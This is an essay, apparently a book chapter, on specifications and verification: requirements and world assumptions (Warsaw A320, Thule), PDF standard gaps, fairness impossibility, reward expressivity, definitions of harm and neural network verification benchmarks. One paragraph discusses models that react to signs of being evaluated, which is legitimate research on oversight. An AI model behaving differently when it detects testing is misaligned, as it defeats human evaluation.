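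Careful wording reduces this problem but doesn't remove it. If Mother(x, y) means "x is the mother of y", readers won't know whether to include stepmothers. "Natural mother" is unclear about surrogacy. Jackson settles on "genetic mother", but points out that even this might fail if genetic engineering ever let a child inherit from several mothers. He thinks a rule for recognising things in the world is bound to be imperfect and only has to be good enough for as long as people use the system. No proof can establish that a designation is right, because it links a formal term to things in the world, which are not formulas.

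Some everyday words are too vague to use as basic terms. In an airline's specification, for example, "flight" might or might not include a cancelled flight, or one that two planes fly in two legs. Jackson instead designates planes, take-offs and landings, and then defines a trip as a take-off followed by the same plane's next landing.

A definition only introduces an abbreviation, so it can't be false. Suppose a warehouse defines its *expected stock* as everything that has come in minus everything that has gone out. It also designates its *actual stock* as the number of items on the premises. The claim that the two are equal is an assumption about the world, and it can be false if items are stolen.

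An indicator on a control panel at the Three Mile Island nuclear plant showed that a valve was shut when it was open, which contributed to the 1979 accident. The indicator actually showed whether current was flowing in the electromagnet that moved the valve. Jackson thinks the mistake was easy to make because nobody had written down what "the valve is shut" referred to.

S is usually easier to make exact than R. For example, engineers have designed the keyboard so that there is no doubt about whether someone hit a key, whereas people may disagree about whether one car hit another.

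### Reverse thrust on a wet runway

Jackson's best-known example is the braking of an aircraft. After landing, pilots slow the plane partly by reversing the thrust of its engines, which would be very dangerous in the air. The software should therefore allow reverse thrust only on the ground. Atlee, Berry and colleagues (2020), in *Software Requirements Specification & Analysis*, write the example out as follows, with "iff" short for "if and only if":

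- R: reverse thrust is enabled iff the aircraft is moving on the runway.
- S: reverse thrust is enabled iff the machine detects pulses from the wheel sensor.
- W₁: the sensor sends pulses iff the wheels are turning.
- W₂: the wheels are turning iff the aircraft is moving on the runway.

R follows by substituting equivalent statements. By S, reverse thrust is enabled if and only if there are pulses. By W₁, there are pulses if and only if the wheels are turning, and by W₂, the wheels are turning if and only if the aircraft is moving on the runway.

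Now suppose that the runway is wet and the aircraft *aquaplanes*, which means that its tyres slide on a film of water without turning.

| | Dry runway | Aquaplaning |
|---|---|---|
| Aircraft moving on the runway | yes | yes |
| Wheels turning | yes | no |
| Sensor pulses | yes | no |
| Reverse thrust enabled | yes | no |
| S | true | true |
| W₁ | true | true |
| W₂ | true | false |
| R | true | false |

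The program does exactly what its specification requires, but the pilots can't use reverse thrust when they need it. The deduction of R is still valid, because it guarantees R only when S, W₁ and W₂ are all true. W₂ can also fail after take-off, because the wheels may keep spinning for a while. The same specification would then allow reverse thrust in the air.

### What happened at Warsaw

The example comes from the crash of Lufthansa flight 2904, an Airbus A320 that overran the runway at Warsaw on 14 September 1993. Aviation Safety Network's *Accident Airbus A320-211 D-AIPN, Tuesday 14 September 1993* records two deaths among the 70 people on board. According to *The A320 Accident in Warsaw*, the plane landed rather fast in a thunderstorm. For 9 seconds after touchdown the pilots could not get any of the braking mechanisms to work, and the wheel brakes took 13 seconds to take effect. The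 plane ran off the end of the runway and over an earth bank.

The real logic was more careful than the textbook version. It required either both main wheels on the ground, or one on the ground and a wheel speed of 72 knots (Leyman 1996, *Engineering Analysis of the Landing Sequence*). The tower had warned the crew of sudden changes in the wind, so they had increased their approach speed, as the manual instructed. *Extracts from the Warsaw Accident Report* describes a touchdown too light to compress the left leg of the landing gear enough for the computer to recognise a landing. With about 3 millimetres of water on the runway, the wheels didn't reach the required speed either.

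So the false assumption was something like "an aircraft that has landed presses down on both legs, or on one leg with its wheels turning fast". This has the same form as Jackson's example, though the details differ. Van Lamsweerde, in *From Worlds to Machines*, writes only that a wrong assumption about turning wheels "might have" led to the accident. The official investigation named the braking logic as a contributory factor, along with others such as the speed and the weather, so better logic alone might not have stopped the plane in time.

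It is also hard to say which part was at fault. Ladkin reports that Mellor pointed out that engineers could have changed the software or made the landing gear switch close under a lighter load. The first would change S, and the second would make the original assumption true more often.

### The moon over Thule

Brian Cantwell Smith, a philosopher and computer scientist, had made a broader argument eight years before the crash. *The Limits of Correctness* (Smith, 1985) opens with a false alarm on 5 October 1960, when the American early-warning station at Thule, Greenland, indicated that many Soviet missiles were heading for the United States. The moon had risen and was reflecting the station's radar signals. Officials assessing the threat doubted the warning, partly because the system was new and the Soviet leader was in New York. Smith's account relies on newspaper stories from that December,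 which he cites from a later book.

Smith argues that developers first form a simplified description of the world, which he calls a model, and then write both the program and the specification in its terms. A proof shows that the program and the specification agree. It doesn't compare the model with the world, and Smith says that nobody has a theory of that relationship. He therefore wanted computer scientists to replace the word "correctness" with "relative consistency". In 1960, an American warning system mistook the rising moon for a Soviet missile attack, and Smith saw no reason to expect that a proof would have revealed the problem. Simulations have the same weakness, because programmers build them from the same model. The model is tested only when the system is used in its real surroundings, and nobody could test a defence against nuclear missiles that way.

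Smith imagines a contract for refrigerators that specifies a temperature of 3 to 6 degrees, a maximum power and a volume. A supplier could meet it with a refrigerator that flings projectiles when someone opens the door, because the requirements (R, in Zave and Jackson's terms) don't rule that out. A customer could also put a running toaster inside and complain about the temperature, because the contract's assumptions about the world (W) are incomplete.

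This distinction also weakens Smith's conclusion about the moon. Suppose R is "the station reports an attack iff missiles are approaching", and S is "the station reports an attack iff the radar receives echoes of a certain pattern". R doesn't follow from S. To complete the proof, the developers must add the assumption that missiles, and nothing else, produce such echoes. They might still not have thought of the moon, but an astronomer could have read the false assumption and objected to it. Smith is right about proofs whose specifications never mention missiles, but proving a requirement about the world at least forces people to write down the assumptions the proof needs.

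Ladkin (1996), in *Limiting Program Verification*, rejects Smith's claim that every abstraction does "violence" to its subject. The statement that a jacket is red is no less true because it leaves out the size. Ladkin also argues that people could not tell what a description describes without some access to the thing itself, and with that access they can sometimes specify the thing directly. For example, they can state the exact requirement for a program that finds the greatest common divisor of two small numbers, because it concerns only numbers. To allow for broken hardware, the specification can read "either the hardware has failed or the answer is right".

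Ladkin is right that leaving things out is harmless in itself. The station's designers could have safely ignored the moon if they had claimed only that missiles produce echoes. Their mistake was to claim also that nothing else does, which is a claim about everything they left out. Most useful requirements seem to need an assumption of this kind, because a missile warning system is not much use if it also reports every moonrise.

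### Do accidents come from bad requirements?

Nancy Leveson, a leading researcher on software safety, wrote in her magazine column "Are You Sure Your Software Will Not Kill Anyone?" that "virtually all accidents involving software stem from unsafe requirements." E. G. Daylight quotes this claim along with two supporting arguments. The first, from Smith, is that formal verification shows only that two formal descriptions are consistent with each other. The second is that complex physical systems have no complete discrete mathematical descriptions.

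These arguments explain how verified software could cause an accident, but they don't show how many accidents happen that way. Finding out would require classifying a set of accidents by the same rule, after selecting them without regard to their causes. Warsaw and Thule fit Leveson's claim, but they are famous because they illustrate it, and Thule was a false alarm rather than an accident. Jackson shares much of Leveson's outlook but gives a case against her claim. He attributes the failures of the Therac-25, a radiotherapy machine, to "relatively straightforward programming errors", and cites an investigation that Leveson co-wrote.

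"Virtually all" allows for exceptions, but the claim also depends on how people classify causes. Someone could say that the Therac-25's requirements should have demanded a device to cut off the beam whatever the program did, and almost any accident can be classified as a requirements failure by the same reasoning. The verified distributed systems discussed earlier show the same ambiguity. Only two of their 16 bugs were in specifications, but others came from false assumptions about the operating system or the network. All 16 were also bugs that researchers went looking for, not accidents.

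Leveson's claim is most plausible for systems such as aircraft, where developers test and review the code thoroughly enough to remove most ordinary programming errors. The remaining errors then tend to be in R and W. If so, the high share is partly a result of good programming, and developers should not take it as a reason to be less careful with the code.

### Questioning the assumptions

The usual reply to Smith and Leveson is that all engineering rests on assumptions that nobody can prove, as Barwise said of applied mathematics in general. Ladkin likewise notes that matching requirements to what people want is difficult outside computing too, though he thinks it is harder for computers than for bridges. The assumptions may still be false, but people who have written them down as W can look for ways in which they might be. seL4's published list of what its proofs assume is a W of this sort,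 with the rest of the computer as the environment.

Van Lamsweerde describes a method called *obstacle analysis*, in which engineers negate an assumption and search for conditions that would make the negation true. In his example, a car should release its handbrake when the driver wants to start. The software can't detect what the driver wants, so it releases the brake when the engine speed rises. This assumes that the engine speed rises only when the driver presses the accelerator. Negating the assumption gives "the engine speed rises and nobody has pressed the accelerator". This can happen when the air conditioning starts, which is very likely on a hot day. The engineers could then exclude that case or give the driver a button.

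The search depends on people who know about cars. *Domain Knowledge in Requirements Engineering* (2025), a survey of research, likewise finds that checking requirements depends heavily on knowledge of the field. Van Lamsweerde also separates assumptions by how reliable they are. A law of nature won't change, but "nobody uses the handbrake below −50 degrees" might be false, and "the driver presses the accelerator to start" may require instructions to drivers.

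People can also monitor an assumption while the system runs. The warehouse can count its stock and compare the count with the expected figure. Two pushes in a row without an entry would refute the assumption about the turnstile. An aircraft could compare its wheel speed with another measurement of its speed over the ground, although this would rely on an assumption about the second instrument. A monitor also has to report the failure early enough to be of use, and at Warsaw a delay of 9 seconds was too long.

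Writing W down also creates a temptation, because a developer can make any failed proof succeed by adding assumptions. In the extreme case, W could include R. W could also contradict itself, and then every requirement would follow from it. Atlee and colleagues therefore ask developers to check that W and S are consistent with each other. When a proof fails, they allow developers to strengthen S, weaken R with the customer's agreement, or add an assumption they can show to be valid.

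Showing that an assumption about people holds requires collecting evidence. Atlee and colleagues' specification for traffic lights prevents collisions only if drivers stop at red. A city can't prove that they do, but it can count the drivers who don't and add a few seconds in which all the lights are red.

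## Why do some things have no formal specification?

Writing down assumptions about the world only makes sense if people can also state what they require of it. They can do this for sorting, but there is no generally accepted formal specification of a web browser, a fair risk score or a harmless robot. A specification may be missing because nobody has written it, because people disagree about what it should require, because the concept has unclear boundaries, or because the chosen formal language can't express it. Several of these reasons can apply at once, but each calls for a different remedy.

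### Width or W?

The current PDF standard is about 1,000 pages of English. Small images inside a PDF page come with a list of labelled values, and each label has a full and an abbreviated form, such as Width and W. *Room for Disagreement*, from the formal methods company Galois, reports that the standard did not cover files that contain both forms of a label with different values. Galois traced the gap back to the first version of PDF in 1993. When its researchers made a test file with eight such images, six well-known viewers displayed it in different ways.

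The working group responsible for the standard had several reasonable ways to fill the gap. It could have banned using both forms, since the standard already banned repeating a label. It could also have required viewers to use whichever value came last, or always the full name. The group decided that the abbreviation takes precedence. Nobody could have deduced this rule from the old text, so the group had to choose one, but its choice made the requirement exact.

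The researchers found the gap while writing part of the standard in a formal language, when they tried to simplify it by treating the two forms as one label. Galois finds similar gaps when it writes specifications for clients. In *Specifications Don't Exist*, Dodds of Galois describes asking clients whether their system should allow some behaviour and hearing that they had never thought about it. In such cases, the specification is missing because nobody has made the decision it would record.

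### Five marks of a specifiable system

Dodds thinks most systems have a deeper problem, and that there is reason to believe nobody can write a precise and coherent specification for them. He lists five characteristics that the most useful formal specifications often have:

- They are mathematically clean, so fairly simple mathematics is enough to state them.
- They are easy to reason about, and help people or tools understand the system.
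- They are encapsulated, which means that the system has a clear boundary and the specification describes what happens there.
- Designers and users broadly agree that the system should match them.
- They change little when the system changes.

Compilers, cryptographic libraries, parsers (programs that read structured data) and small operating system kernels fit this description well, and are also the best-known successes of formal verification. Dodds thinks verifying the compiler GCC would be expensive but feasible, because CompCert has already shown how to build a verified compiler. He thinks nobody could say what to prove about a browser such as Chrome.

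The category "PDF" has no sharp boundary, although the format looked easy to specify because it has a well-maintained standard, a huge supply of examples and about 60 viewers. People tend to blame the viewer when a file doesn't open, so viewers try to repair files that break the standard, and each does this slightly differently. The viewers' developers disagree about how to treat a faulty file. According to Dodds, a large collection will contain some files that clearly conform to the standard and some that attackers clearly designed to do damage, but for most files nobody knows whether they are good or bad.

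DARPA, the US military's research agency, ran a programme called SafeDocs from 2018 to 2023 to make such formats safer. As part of it, Galois spent several years on a formal definition of PDF. Dodds is proud of the work but calls the result "non-descriptive", because it differs from what real viewers do, and "non-normative", because it doesn't capture what the team thinks viewers should do.

DARPA (2023) is more positive, reporting that the programme's researchers had proposed 117 clarifications to the standard and that the standards body ISO had approved solutions for 88. *Daedalus* (2024), a paper on the language Galois used, reports that a reference parser built with the PDF Association was the only one in which a team of simulated attackers found no defects.

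These accounts are compatible, since people can define a format exactly and write a good program for it even if most files in circulation break the rules. But they also suggest that Dodds overstates his case. The project did produce a precise definition, but the definition lacked the "correctness jurisdiction" that Turner thinks makes a description a specification, because developers of popular viewers had little reason to change them to match it. The PDF Association also reports changing the standard in several places to match what existing software did.

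### Two exact definitions of fairness

People can also disagree when every proposal is exact. Some American courts use scores that predict whether a defendant will commit another crime. Journalists at ProPublica investigated one of these scores, COMPAS, and concluded that it was biased against black defendants. Among people who did not reoffend, black defendants were nearly twice as likely as white defendants to have a high-risk score. Northpointe, the company behind COMPAS, replied that a high-risk score meant the same thing for both groups, since about the same share of high-scoring people in each group went on to reoffend.

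Chouldechova (2017), in *Fair prediction with disparate impact*, shows that both sides could be right about the numbers. Her argument uses four quantities for each group:

- p, the *base rate*, is the share of the group who reoffend.
- PPV, the *positive predictive value*, is the share of people with high-risk scores who reoffend.
- FNR, the *false negative rate*, is the share of reoffenders with low-risk scores.
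- FPR, the *false positive rate*, is the share of non-reoffenders with high-risk scores.

It seems reasonable to demand that PPV, FNR and FPR each be equal for the two groups. But in a group of N people, pN reoffend, and pN(1 − FNR) of these have high-risk scores. They make up a share PPV of everyone with a high-risk score, so the number of false alarms is pN(1 − FNR) · (1 − PPV)/PPV. Dividing by the (1 − p)N people who don't reoffend gives

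FPR = p/(1 − p) · (1 − PPV)/PPV · (1 − FNR)

If two groups have the same PPV and FNR but different base rates, their false positive rates must differ. The table shows two groups of 1,000 people, each with a PPV of 0.8 and an FNR of 0.2.

| | Base rate 50% | Base rate 20% |
|---|---|---|
| Reoffenders | 500 | 200 |
| Reoffenders with a high-risk score | 400 | 160 |
| Everyone with a high-risk score | 500 | 200 |
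| Non-reoffenders with a high-risk score | 100 of 500 | 40 of 800 |
| False positive rate | 20% | 5% |

The only useful exception is a score that never gives a false alarm, because then PPV is 1 and FPR is 0 in both groups. In the COMPAS data from Broward County, Florida, 51% of black and 39% of white defendants reoffended. If PPV and FNR were equal across the two groups, the FPR would be about 1.6 times as high for black defendants. The actual gap was larger because COMPAS also missed a smaller share of black reoffenders, and a lower FNR raises the FPR.

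A programmer could write any of the three demands as a formula and check a score against it. Together, they make a specification that no realistic program can meet, like those in *Vero* that allowed inconsistent orderings. A proof can show that the demands conflict, but it doesn't determine which one to drop. Chouldechova calls fairness "a social and ethical concept, not a statistical one", and the choice depends partly on how people use the score. A false alarm does more damage if a high-risk score leads to a longer sentence than if it leads to extra support.

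### A task that no reward can express

Sometimes everyone agrees on a task and can state it in one line, but not in the language their tools require. In *reinforcement learning*, an AI agent learns by trial and error to collect as much reward as possible. According to the *reward hypothesis*, any goal can be expressed as maximising a sum of numerical rewards. In *On the Expressivity of Markov Reward* (2021), Abel, Dabney and colleagues tested this idea for *Markov* rewards, which depend only on the current state, the agent's action and the next state.

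Suppose an agent goes back and forth between rooms A and B, and in each room it presses either a left or a right button. Its task is to press the same button in both rooms. As a formula, this is just action(A) = action(B). A *policy* fixes an action for each state, so there are four policies: LL, RR, LR and RL, where the first letter is the button in room A. Write a(L) and a(R) for the rewards in room A, and b(L) and b(R) for those in room B. For one trip through both rooms:

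1. LL earns a(L) + b(L), and RR earns a(R) + b(R).
2. LR earns a(L) + b(R), and RL earns a(R) + b(L).
3. Each pair of policies uses all four rewards once, so LL and RR together earn exactly as much as LR and RL together.
4. If LL and RR both earn the maximum m, then LR and RL together earn 2m. Neither can earn more than m, so both earn m.

Therefore, no choice of rewards can make LL and RR the only best policies. Letting LL and RR earn different amounts doesn't help either. If each earned more than both LR and RL, the sum for LL and RR would be larger than the sum for LR and RL, which contradicts step 3. Abel and colleagues use the opposite task, in which the agent must take different actions in the two states, and mention a robot on a grid that should always move in the same direction.

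Another of their counterexamples matters less. It requires a reward that makes one policy better than another, but *Settling the Reward Hypothesis* (2022) points out that the two policies differ only in a state that the agent never reaches under either.

Abel and colleagues also found an efficient algorithm that, for any finite environment and any task of the kinds they study, either constructs a suitable reward or shows that none exists. They ran it on randomly chosen sets of acceptable policies in small environments, typically with four states and three actions. In nearly every setting they tried, some of the sets had no suitable reward, so the problem isn't limited to contrived cases. However, random sets of policies may not resemble tasks that people care about.

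Giving the agent a memory solves the two-room problem. If the state includes the last button it pressed, a developer can reward it for pressing the same one again. *Reward machines* generalize this by recording relevant past events in a finite number of memory states. But *Learning Optimal and Sample-Efficient Decision Policies with Guarantees* (2026) notes that reward machines can't express requirements about infinite runs, which linear temporal logic can. Richer languages can let rewards depend on the whole history, but Abel and colleagues warn that such rewards may be very hard to learn from, because the number of possible histories grows so quickly with their length.

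Another remedy is to use several rewards at once. *On the Expressivity of Multidimensional Markov Reward* (2023) proves that for any set of deterministic policies, some combination of Markov rewards characterises it. For the two rooms, one score could add 1 for pressing left in A and subtract 1 for pressing left in B, and a second score could do the reverse. Only LL and RR would keep both scores from going negative.

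Skalse and Abate (2024), in *On the Limitations of Markovian Rewards*, show that a single reward can't express most tasks of three kinds: those with several objectives, those that are sensitive to risk, and "modal" tasks, which concern what the agent could do as well as what it does. One modal task is never to enter a room that the agent couldn't leave again. These theorems concern only one formal language, so they give no reason to think that such tasks are beyond mathematics.

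### What counts as harm?

A richer formal language doesn't help if people can't say what they want to specify. According to *A Causal Analysis of Harm* (2022), the proposal for the EU's AI Act contained more than 25 references to "harm" or "harmful". The paper also quotes a description of the notion of harm as a "Frankensteinian jumble".

Researchers have written exact definitions of harm, which *The Limits of Predicting Agents from Behaviour* (2025) divides into two groups. On *counterfactual* accounts, a decision harms a person if and only if that person would have been better off without it. On *causal* accounts, the decision must be a cause of the harm. Suppose a nurse makes a patient ill by giving him the wrong drug, but a colleague would have given him the same drug if she hadn't. She didn't harm him on a counterfactual account, because he would have been no better off without her decision,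 but she did on a causal account, because her decision caused his illness.

*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024) suggests a causal definition of harm as a starting point for safety specifications. Roughly, an event harms someone if it causes an outcome worse than a default level of well-being, and some alternative event would have led to a better outcome. The definition is exact once somebody has chosen the default, but the formula doesn't determine which default to choose. Suppose a company gives a pupil a free AI tutor for a year and then withdraws it. The company has harmed her if the default is life with the tutor, but not if the default is life without one.

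People also have to compare and add up harms. *Quantifying Harm* (2022) points out that knowing the harm to each individual does not settle how to calculate the total. A specification that permits either one broken leg or a thousand headaches, but not both, needs a rule for how many headaches equal one broken leg.

Young (2025), in *On the Computational, Informational, and Physical Foundations for AI Safety*, makes the more general claim that any specification of "harm" must be incomplete. The paper is a three-page summary of ongoing work without a full proof. Young treats the true answer to whether something is harmful as a random variable O, and the AI's specification as a random variable I. The *entropy* H(O) measures how uncertain the answer is before anyone consults the specification, in bits. The *mutual information* I(O; I) measures how much of that uncertainty the specification removes.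 Young's theorem is that, for an external and ambiguous concept with H(O) > 0,

I(O; I) < H(O)

Young derives this from the "externality" of the concept and the *data processing inequality*, the theorem that processing a signal can't add information about its source.

I(O; I) can never be greater than H(O), and the two are equal exactly when the specification settles every answer. They can be equal even when H(O) is positive. For example, whether an email has more than 100 characters varies from one email to the next, so it has positive entropy, but a one-line program always gets it right. The data processing inequality only gives "at most", not "less than". The strict inequality must therefore come from externality, which has to mean that no specification fully determines what is harmful. That is what Young set out to show, so the argument is circular.

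Suppose we ask a randomly chosen member of a panel whether a randomly chosen action is harmful. In 45% of cases the whole panel agrees that it is, in 45% the whole panel agrees that it isn't, and in the other 10% the panel splits evenly. Half of all answers are then "harmful", so H(O) is 1 bit. A specification that perfectly sorts cases into "harmful", "harmless" and "disputed" still leaves 1 bit of uncertainty in each disputed case, or 0.1 bits on average across all cases, so I(O; I) is 0.9. The missing 0.1 bits come from the panel's disagreement, and improving the specification would not remove them. So the inequality seems to show only that an ambiguous concept stays ambiguous, and it doesn't give the size of the gap.

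Young proposes the ratio I(O; I)/H(O) as a measure of alignment, but a specification can prevent harm without predicting what people will call harmful. A specification that forbids a robot to move at all prevents every injury the robot could cause by moving, yet its ratio is zero because it gives every movement the same verdict. Young's practical proposal would similarly prevent harm by using hardware to limit a robot's speed, force and reach, whatever its software does.

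### Working without a complete specification

Developers can often specify part of a system's behaviour even when they can't specify all of it. For example, the compiler for the programming language Rust checks that a program written in the safe part of the language will not cause memory errors, but a program that passes can still delete the wrong file. A test case is even narrower because it covers only one input, but Dodds points out that it is immediately useful and takes little effort to write. These *partial specifications* place no requirements on the behaviour they leave out.

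Another option is to substitute an exact rule that forbids more than necessary. Galois' *Building DaeDaLus and ICARUS* suggests that organisations could define a restricted version of PDF for internal use, for instance one without JavaScript, which lets a document contain small programs. Like the program checkers described earlier, this rule would reject some harmless cases, such as an order form that uses JavaScript to add up prices.

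A stand-in is only cautious if it covers everything dangerous, and people can't be sure it does unless they know what the dangers are. A file without JavaScript could still exploit a bug in the way a viewer reads images, and a robot that can't move fast or press hard could still hand a patient the wrong medicine.

Developers can also learn a specification from examples, as they do when they train a network on photographs labelled "pedestrian". In formal logic, a person can write part of a formula, leave gaps, and supply examples of good and bad behaviour. An algorithm then fills the gaps so that the formula fits the examples. This is easier than writing the whole formula, because people only have to recognise good behaviour. *Specification Engineering* (Chechik, Kang and colleagues), a report on a September 2025 research seminar, describes a talk on this method.

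The drawback is that many specifications usually fit the same examples. Suppose the owner of the email assistant marks replies after 5 and 20 minutes as prompt and a reply after 3 hours as late. Any limit from 20 minutes up to 3 hours fits. More examples would narrow the range, but someone still has to decide about the cases in between.

Inferring an AI model's aims from its behaviour is harder still. In the preprint *On the Limits of Behavioral Alignment*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) uses the term *normative indistinguishability* for cases where different hypotheses about a model's aims predict the same evaluation results. He argues that if a model can react to signs that it is being evaluated, a finite set of tests can identify only a class of hypotheses, and models that fit different members of that class may behave differently outside the tests. Good behaviour in tests therefore can't serve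 as a complete specification of what a model will do, though tests can still reveal violations. The argument doesn't show that good aims are impossible to specify.

Developers can also write rules for AI models in ordinary language. Young mentions constitutions, written principles that a model uses to criticise its own answers. Such rules can cover cases that an exact rule misses. A model that applies the rule "do not mislead the customer" may tell the customer that the parcel was returned to the warehouse, which the rule about matching dates did not require.

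In return, developers give up a fixed meaning. Two careful readers, or two AI models, may disagree about whether an answer is misleading. Nobody can state a theorem without an exact condition, or deduce from a written principle how a trained model will apply it. Participants in the seminar noted that developers increasingly state what they want in natural-language prompts, but thought that unstructured prompts were poorly suited to debugging and maintaining complex software. They also disagreed about what a specification is. Some reserved the word for descriptions of how a system should behave, while others would apply it to nearly anything developers produce, including the code. They agreed to leave the word undefined and discuss the properties a specification can have, such as being formal or readable.

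A developer can combine formal rules with instructions in English. For example, a checker could enforce a formula that limits an email assistant to an approved list of recipients, while "never mislead anyone" stays an instruction in English. The developer could then prove that the assistant only emails people on the list, but not that its messages never mislead them.

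## What can be proved about a neural network?

A car with automatic emergency braking may use a neural network to find pedestrians in its camera pictures. Developers can look up every number the network uses in its calculations, but they have no formula for the answers it should give. With three colour values per pixel and 256 levels per value, there are 256 to the power of 1,800,000 possible pictures of 1,000 by 600 pixels, a number with more than four million digits. Nobody has found a condition on the colour values that picks out the pictures that show a pedestrian.

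Researchers who verify networks therefore prove substitutes, which are exact properties that have some connection with recognising pedestrians.

### Robustness, ranges and monotonicity

The most common substitute is *local robustness*. For a chosen picture x and a small number ε, it requires

for all x′ with ‖x′ − x‖ ≤ ε: class(x′) = class(x)

Here ‖x′ − x‖ is the distance between the two pictures, usually measured as the largest change in any single value. A small colour picture of 32 by 32 pixels has 3,072 values. If ε is 1/255 of the brightness range, each value may stay the same or go up or down by one level, so a proof covers more than 10¹⁴⁶⁵ different pictures.

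Other properties restrict the output over a whole region of inputs. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) describes networks that estimate how much longer an aircraft part will last. When the sensor readings are within certain ranges, the estimate must be within an expected range. *Monotonicity* requires that a larger input never give a smaller output. It compares two runs of the network, so it is a hyperproperty, like the rule about secrets. The competition's new specification language can express such comparisons. The verifiers found a counterexample for each of 50 new monotonicity questions about networks that advise aircraft on avoiding collisions.

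Robustness is a poor substitute for correctness, partly because a network can be robust even when its labels are wrong. *No Soundness in the Real World* (Szász, Bánhelyi and Jelasity, 2025) defines robustness relative to the label that the network itself gives to the input x. A network that calls a pedestrian a lamp post, and does the same for every nearby picture, is therefore robust at that picture. A network that answers "no pedestrian" to every picture is robust everywhere, much as the program that always returned the empty list satisfied the sorting specification.

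Researchers can exclude such cases by counting only pictures that the network also labels correctly. The share of test pictures that meet both conditions is the *certified accuracy*. One network in the competition labels 83.5% of its test pictures correctly, and its certified accuracy is 66.0% for changes of up to 2 levels in 255. For a network of the same type trained to withstand changes of up to 8 levels, the figures are 57.2% and 35.5%, so training for larger changes led to more ordinary mistakes. These figures do not guarantee anything about pictures outside the test set.

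Pixel distance is also a poor measure of the changes that matter on a road. If the camera moves slightly to one side, many pixel values may change greatly. One of the benchmarks, MetaRoom, describes camera movements directly, but they are as small as a hundredth of a millimetre. Another benchmark tests whether an image generator draws a car at the requested distance. It uses a second network to estimate the distance in the picture, so a proof shows that the two networks are consistent with each other, but both could be wrong.

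### A network with two units

A very small network is enough to show how verifiers work. It has two inputs, a and b, each between 0 and 1, and computes

y = ReLU(a − b) + ReLU(b − a)

where ReLU(z) is z if z is positive and 0 otherwise. Suppose we want to prove that y is never more than 1.

1. *Interval bounds.* Since a − b lies between −1 and 1, the first unit's output lies between 0 and 1. The same is true of the second unit, so y ≤ 2. This is true but too weak, because the calculation treats the units separately, and they can't both be positive at once.
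2. *Case splitting.* If a ≥ b, the second unit gives 0 and y = a − b, which is at most 1. If a < b, the first unit gives 0 and y = b − a, which is also at most 1. So y ≤ 1 in both cases, and a = 1, b = 0 reaches this bound.
3. *Linear bounds.* For z between −1 and 1, ReLU(z) is never above the straight line (z + 1)/2. Therefore y ≤ (a − b + 1)/2 + (b − a + 1)/2 = 1. Here a and b stay in the formula and cancel, so the verifier doesn't need to split.

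Passing such bounds from layer to layer is called *bound propagation*. It is *sound*, meaning it never proves a false property, but not *complete*, because it may fail to prove a true one. The textbook *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* (2021) says that these methods can make "stupid mistakes" when their bounds are too loose, but that they work well in practice. The best verifiers compute bounds, split the problem in two if the bounds don't settle it, and repeat this for each half.

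With n units that could be either positive or zero, there are up to 2ⁿ cases. The collision-avoidance networks have 300 units, so there could be up to about 2 × 10⁹⁰ cases. When researchers first checked a standard set of properties of these networks, some checks took days and others never finished. In 2026, three verifiers resolved all 186 questions about these networks, with a limit of about two minutes per question.

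No method is likely to be fast on every network, because the problem is *NP-complete*. A fast method for it would yield fast methods for thousands of other problems that people have failed to solve quickly for decades. One of these is 3-SAT, which asks whether some choice of true and false values satisfies a list of clauses such as "p or not q or r". If 1 stands for true and 0 for false, the unit ReLU(q − p − r) gives 1 when this clause is false and 0 otherwise. A network with one such unit per clause can count the false clauses, and further units can rule out inputs between 0 and 1. Proving that the count is never 0 then means proving that no choice satisfies the whole list.

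Unlike the halting problem, this problem is one a computer could always solve given enough time, and many cases are easy. The competition included 100 networks built from random lists of clauses with up to 100 variables, and four verifiers got all of them right.

*Randomized smoothing* does without any analysis of the units. It builds a new classifier, which adds random noise to the picture many times, runs the network on each noisy copy, and returns the most frequent label. Moving the original picture a little shifts the whole cloud of noisy copies, and a small shift can take only a limited amount of probability away from the leading label. For Gaussian noise with standard deviation σ, if the leading label has probability p > ½, the answer can't change within a distance of

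σ · Φ⁻¹(p)

where Φ⁻¹ is the inverse of the normal distribution function and distance is the ordinary Euclidean kind. With σ = 0.25 and p = 0.9, this is about 0.32 on a brightness scale from 0 to 1. It is enough to change all 3,072 values of a small picture by about 1.5 levels in 255. The method suits large networks because it only has to run them. But the guarantee is about the new classifier and not the original network, and people must estimate p from samples, so there is a small chance that a certificate is wrong.

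### What verifiers could prove in 2026

The 2026 Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP) had 24 benchmarks in its main track, up from the 16 reported for 2025 in *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025). Thirteen verifiers competed on 3,373 questions about 467 networks. The winner, α,β-CROWN, settled 3,164 of them, or 94%, with 1,982 proofs and 1,182 counterexamples. Nearly a third of the questions were about text classifiers with roughly 4,000 weights, and without these the winner's share falls to 91%. The runner-up, Vibecheck, settled 3,108. Its developers built it in two months with the AI coding tool Claude Code.

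These percentages depend on the choice of questions. Researchers proposed the benchmarks, the participants voted on which to include, and the time limits had to fit a budget. α,β-CROWN settled only 38 of 60 questions on a benchmark that Ladner and colleagues describe as deliberately challenging.

The largest network, VGG-16, classifies photographs and has 138 million weights. Most of the others have between a few thousand and a few million. α,β-CROWN proved all 18 properties of VGG-16. These properties allow changes to anything from a single pixel to the whole picture, but the benchmark's description doesn't give the size of the changes.

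Small networks can also be hard to verify. Two image classifiers that use *transformers*, the design behind today's language models, have only 68,000 to 76,000 weights. α,β-CROWN proved them robust to changes of one brightness level on 123 of 200 pictures. Another verifier, ACT, reported proofs for all 200, but that result is hard to believe. The benchmark's developers had removed most of the pictures with known counterexamples, so a false claim would probably go unnoticed, and they warn that the benchmark may not reveal unsound verifiers. ACT also received penalties on ten questions elsewhere.

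The results were worse for traffic signs. The best of three networks correctly identifies 96% of German test signs. In 45 robustness checks on the three networks, the verifier α,β-CROWN found counterexamples in 36, and no verifier proved robustness in any.

A verifier's "yes" is also weaker evidence than a proof in Lean, because competitors don't have to supply a proof that can be checked independently. The organisers usually learn that an answer is wrong only if another verifier produces a valid counterexample. Eight of the thirteen verifiers, including the winner, gave at least one answer that was wrong or lacked a valid counterexample. Ladner and colleagues name checkable proofs as a longer-term goal.

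### Language models

A language model with 100 billion weights is over 700 times as large as VGG-16 and more than a million times as large as the transformers in the competition. Memory is one obstacle to verifying a model of that size. Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026) explain in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism* that standard bound propagation must keep its large tables of numbers on a single graphics processor. They spread the tables over several processors, using methods from the training of large models.

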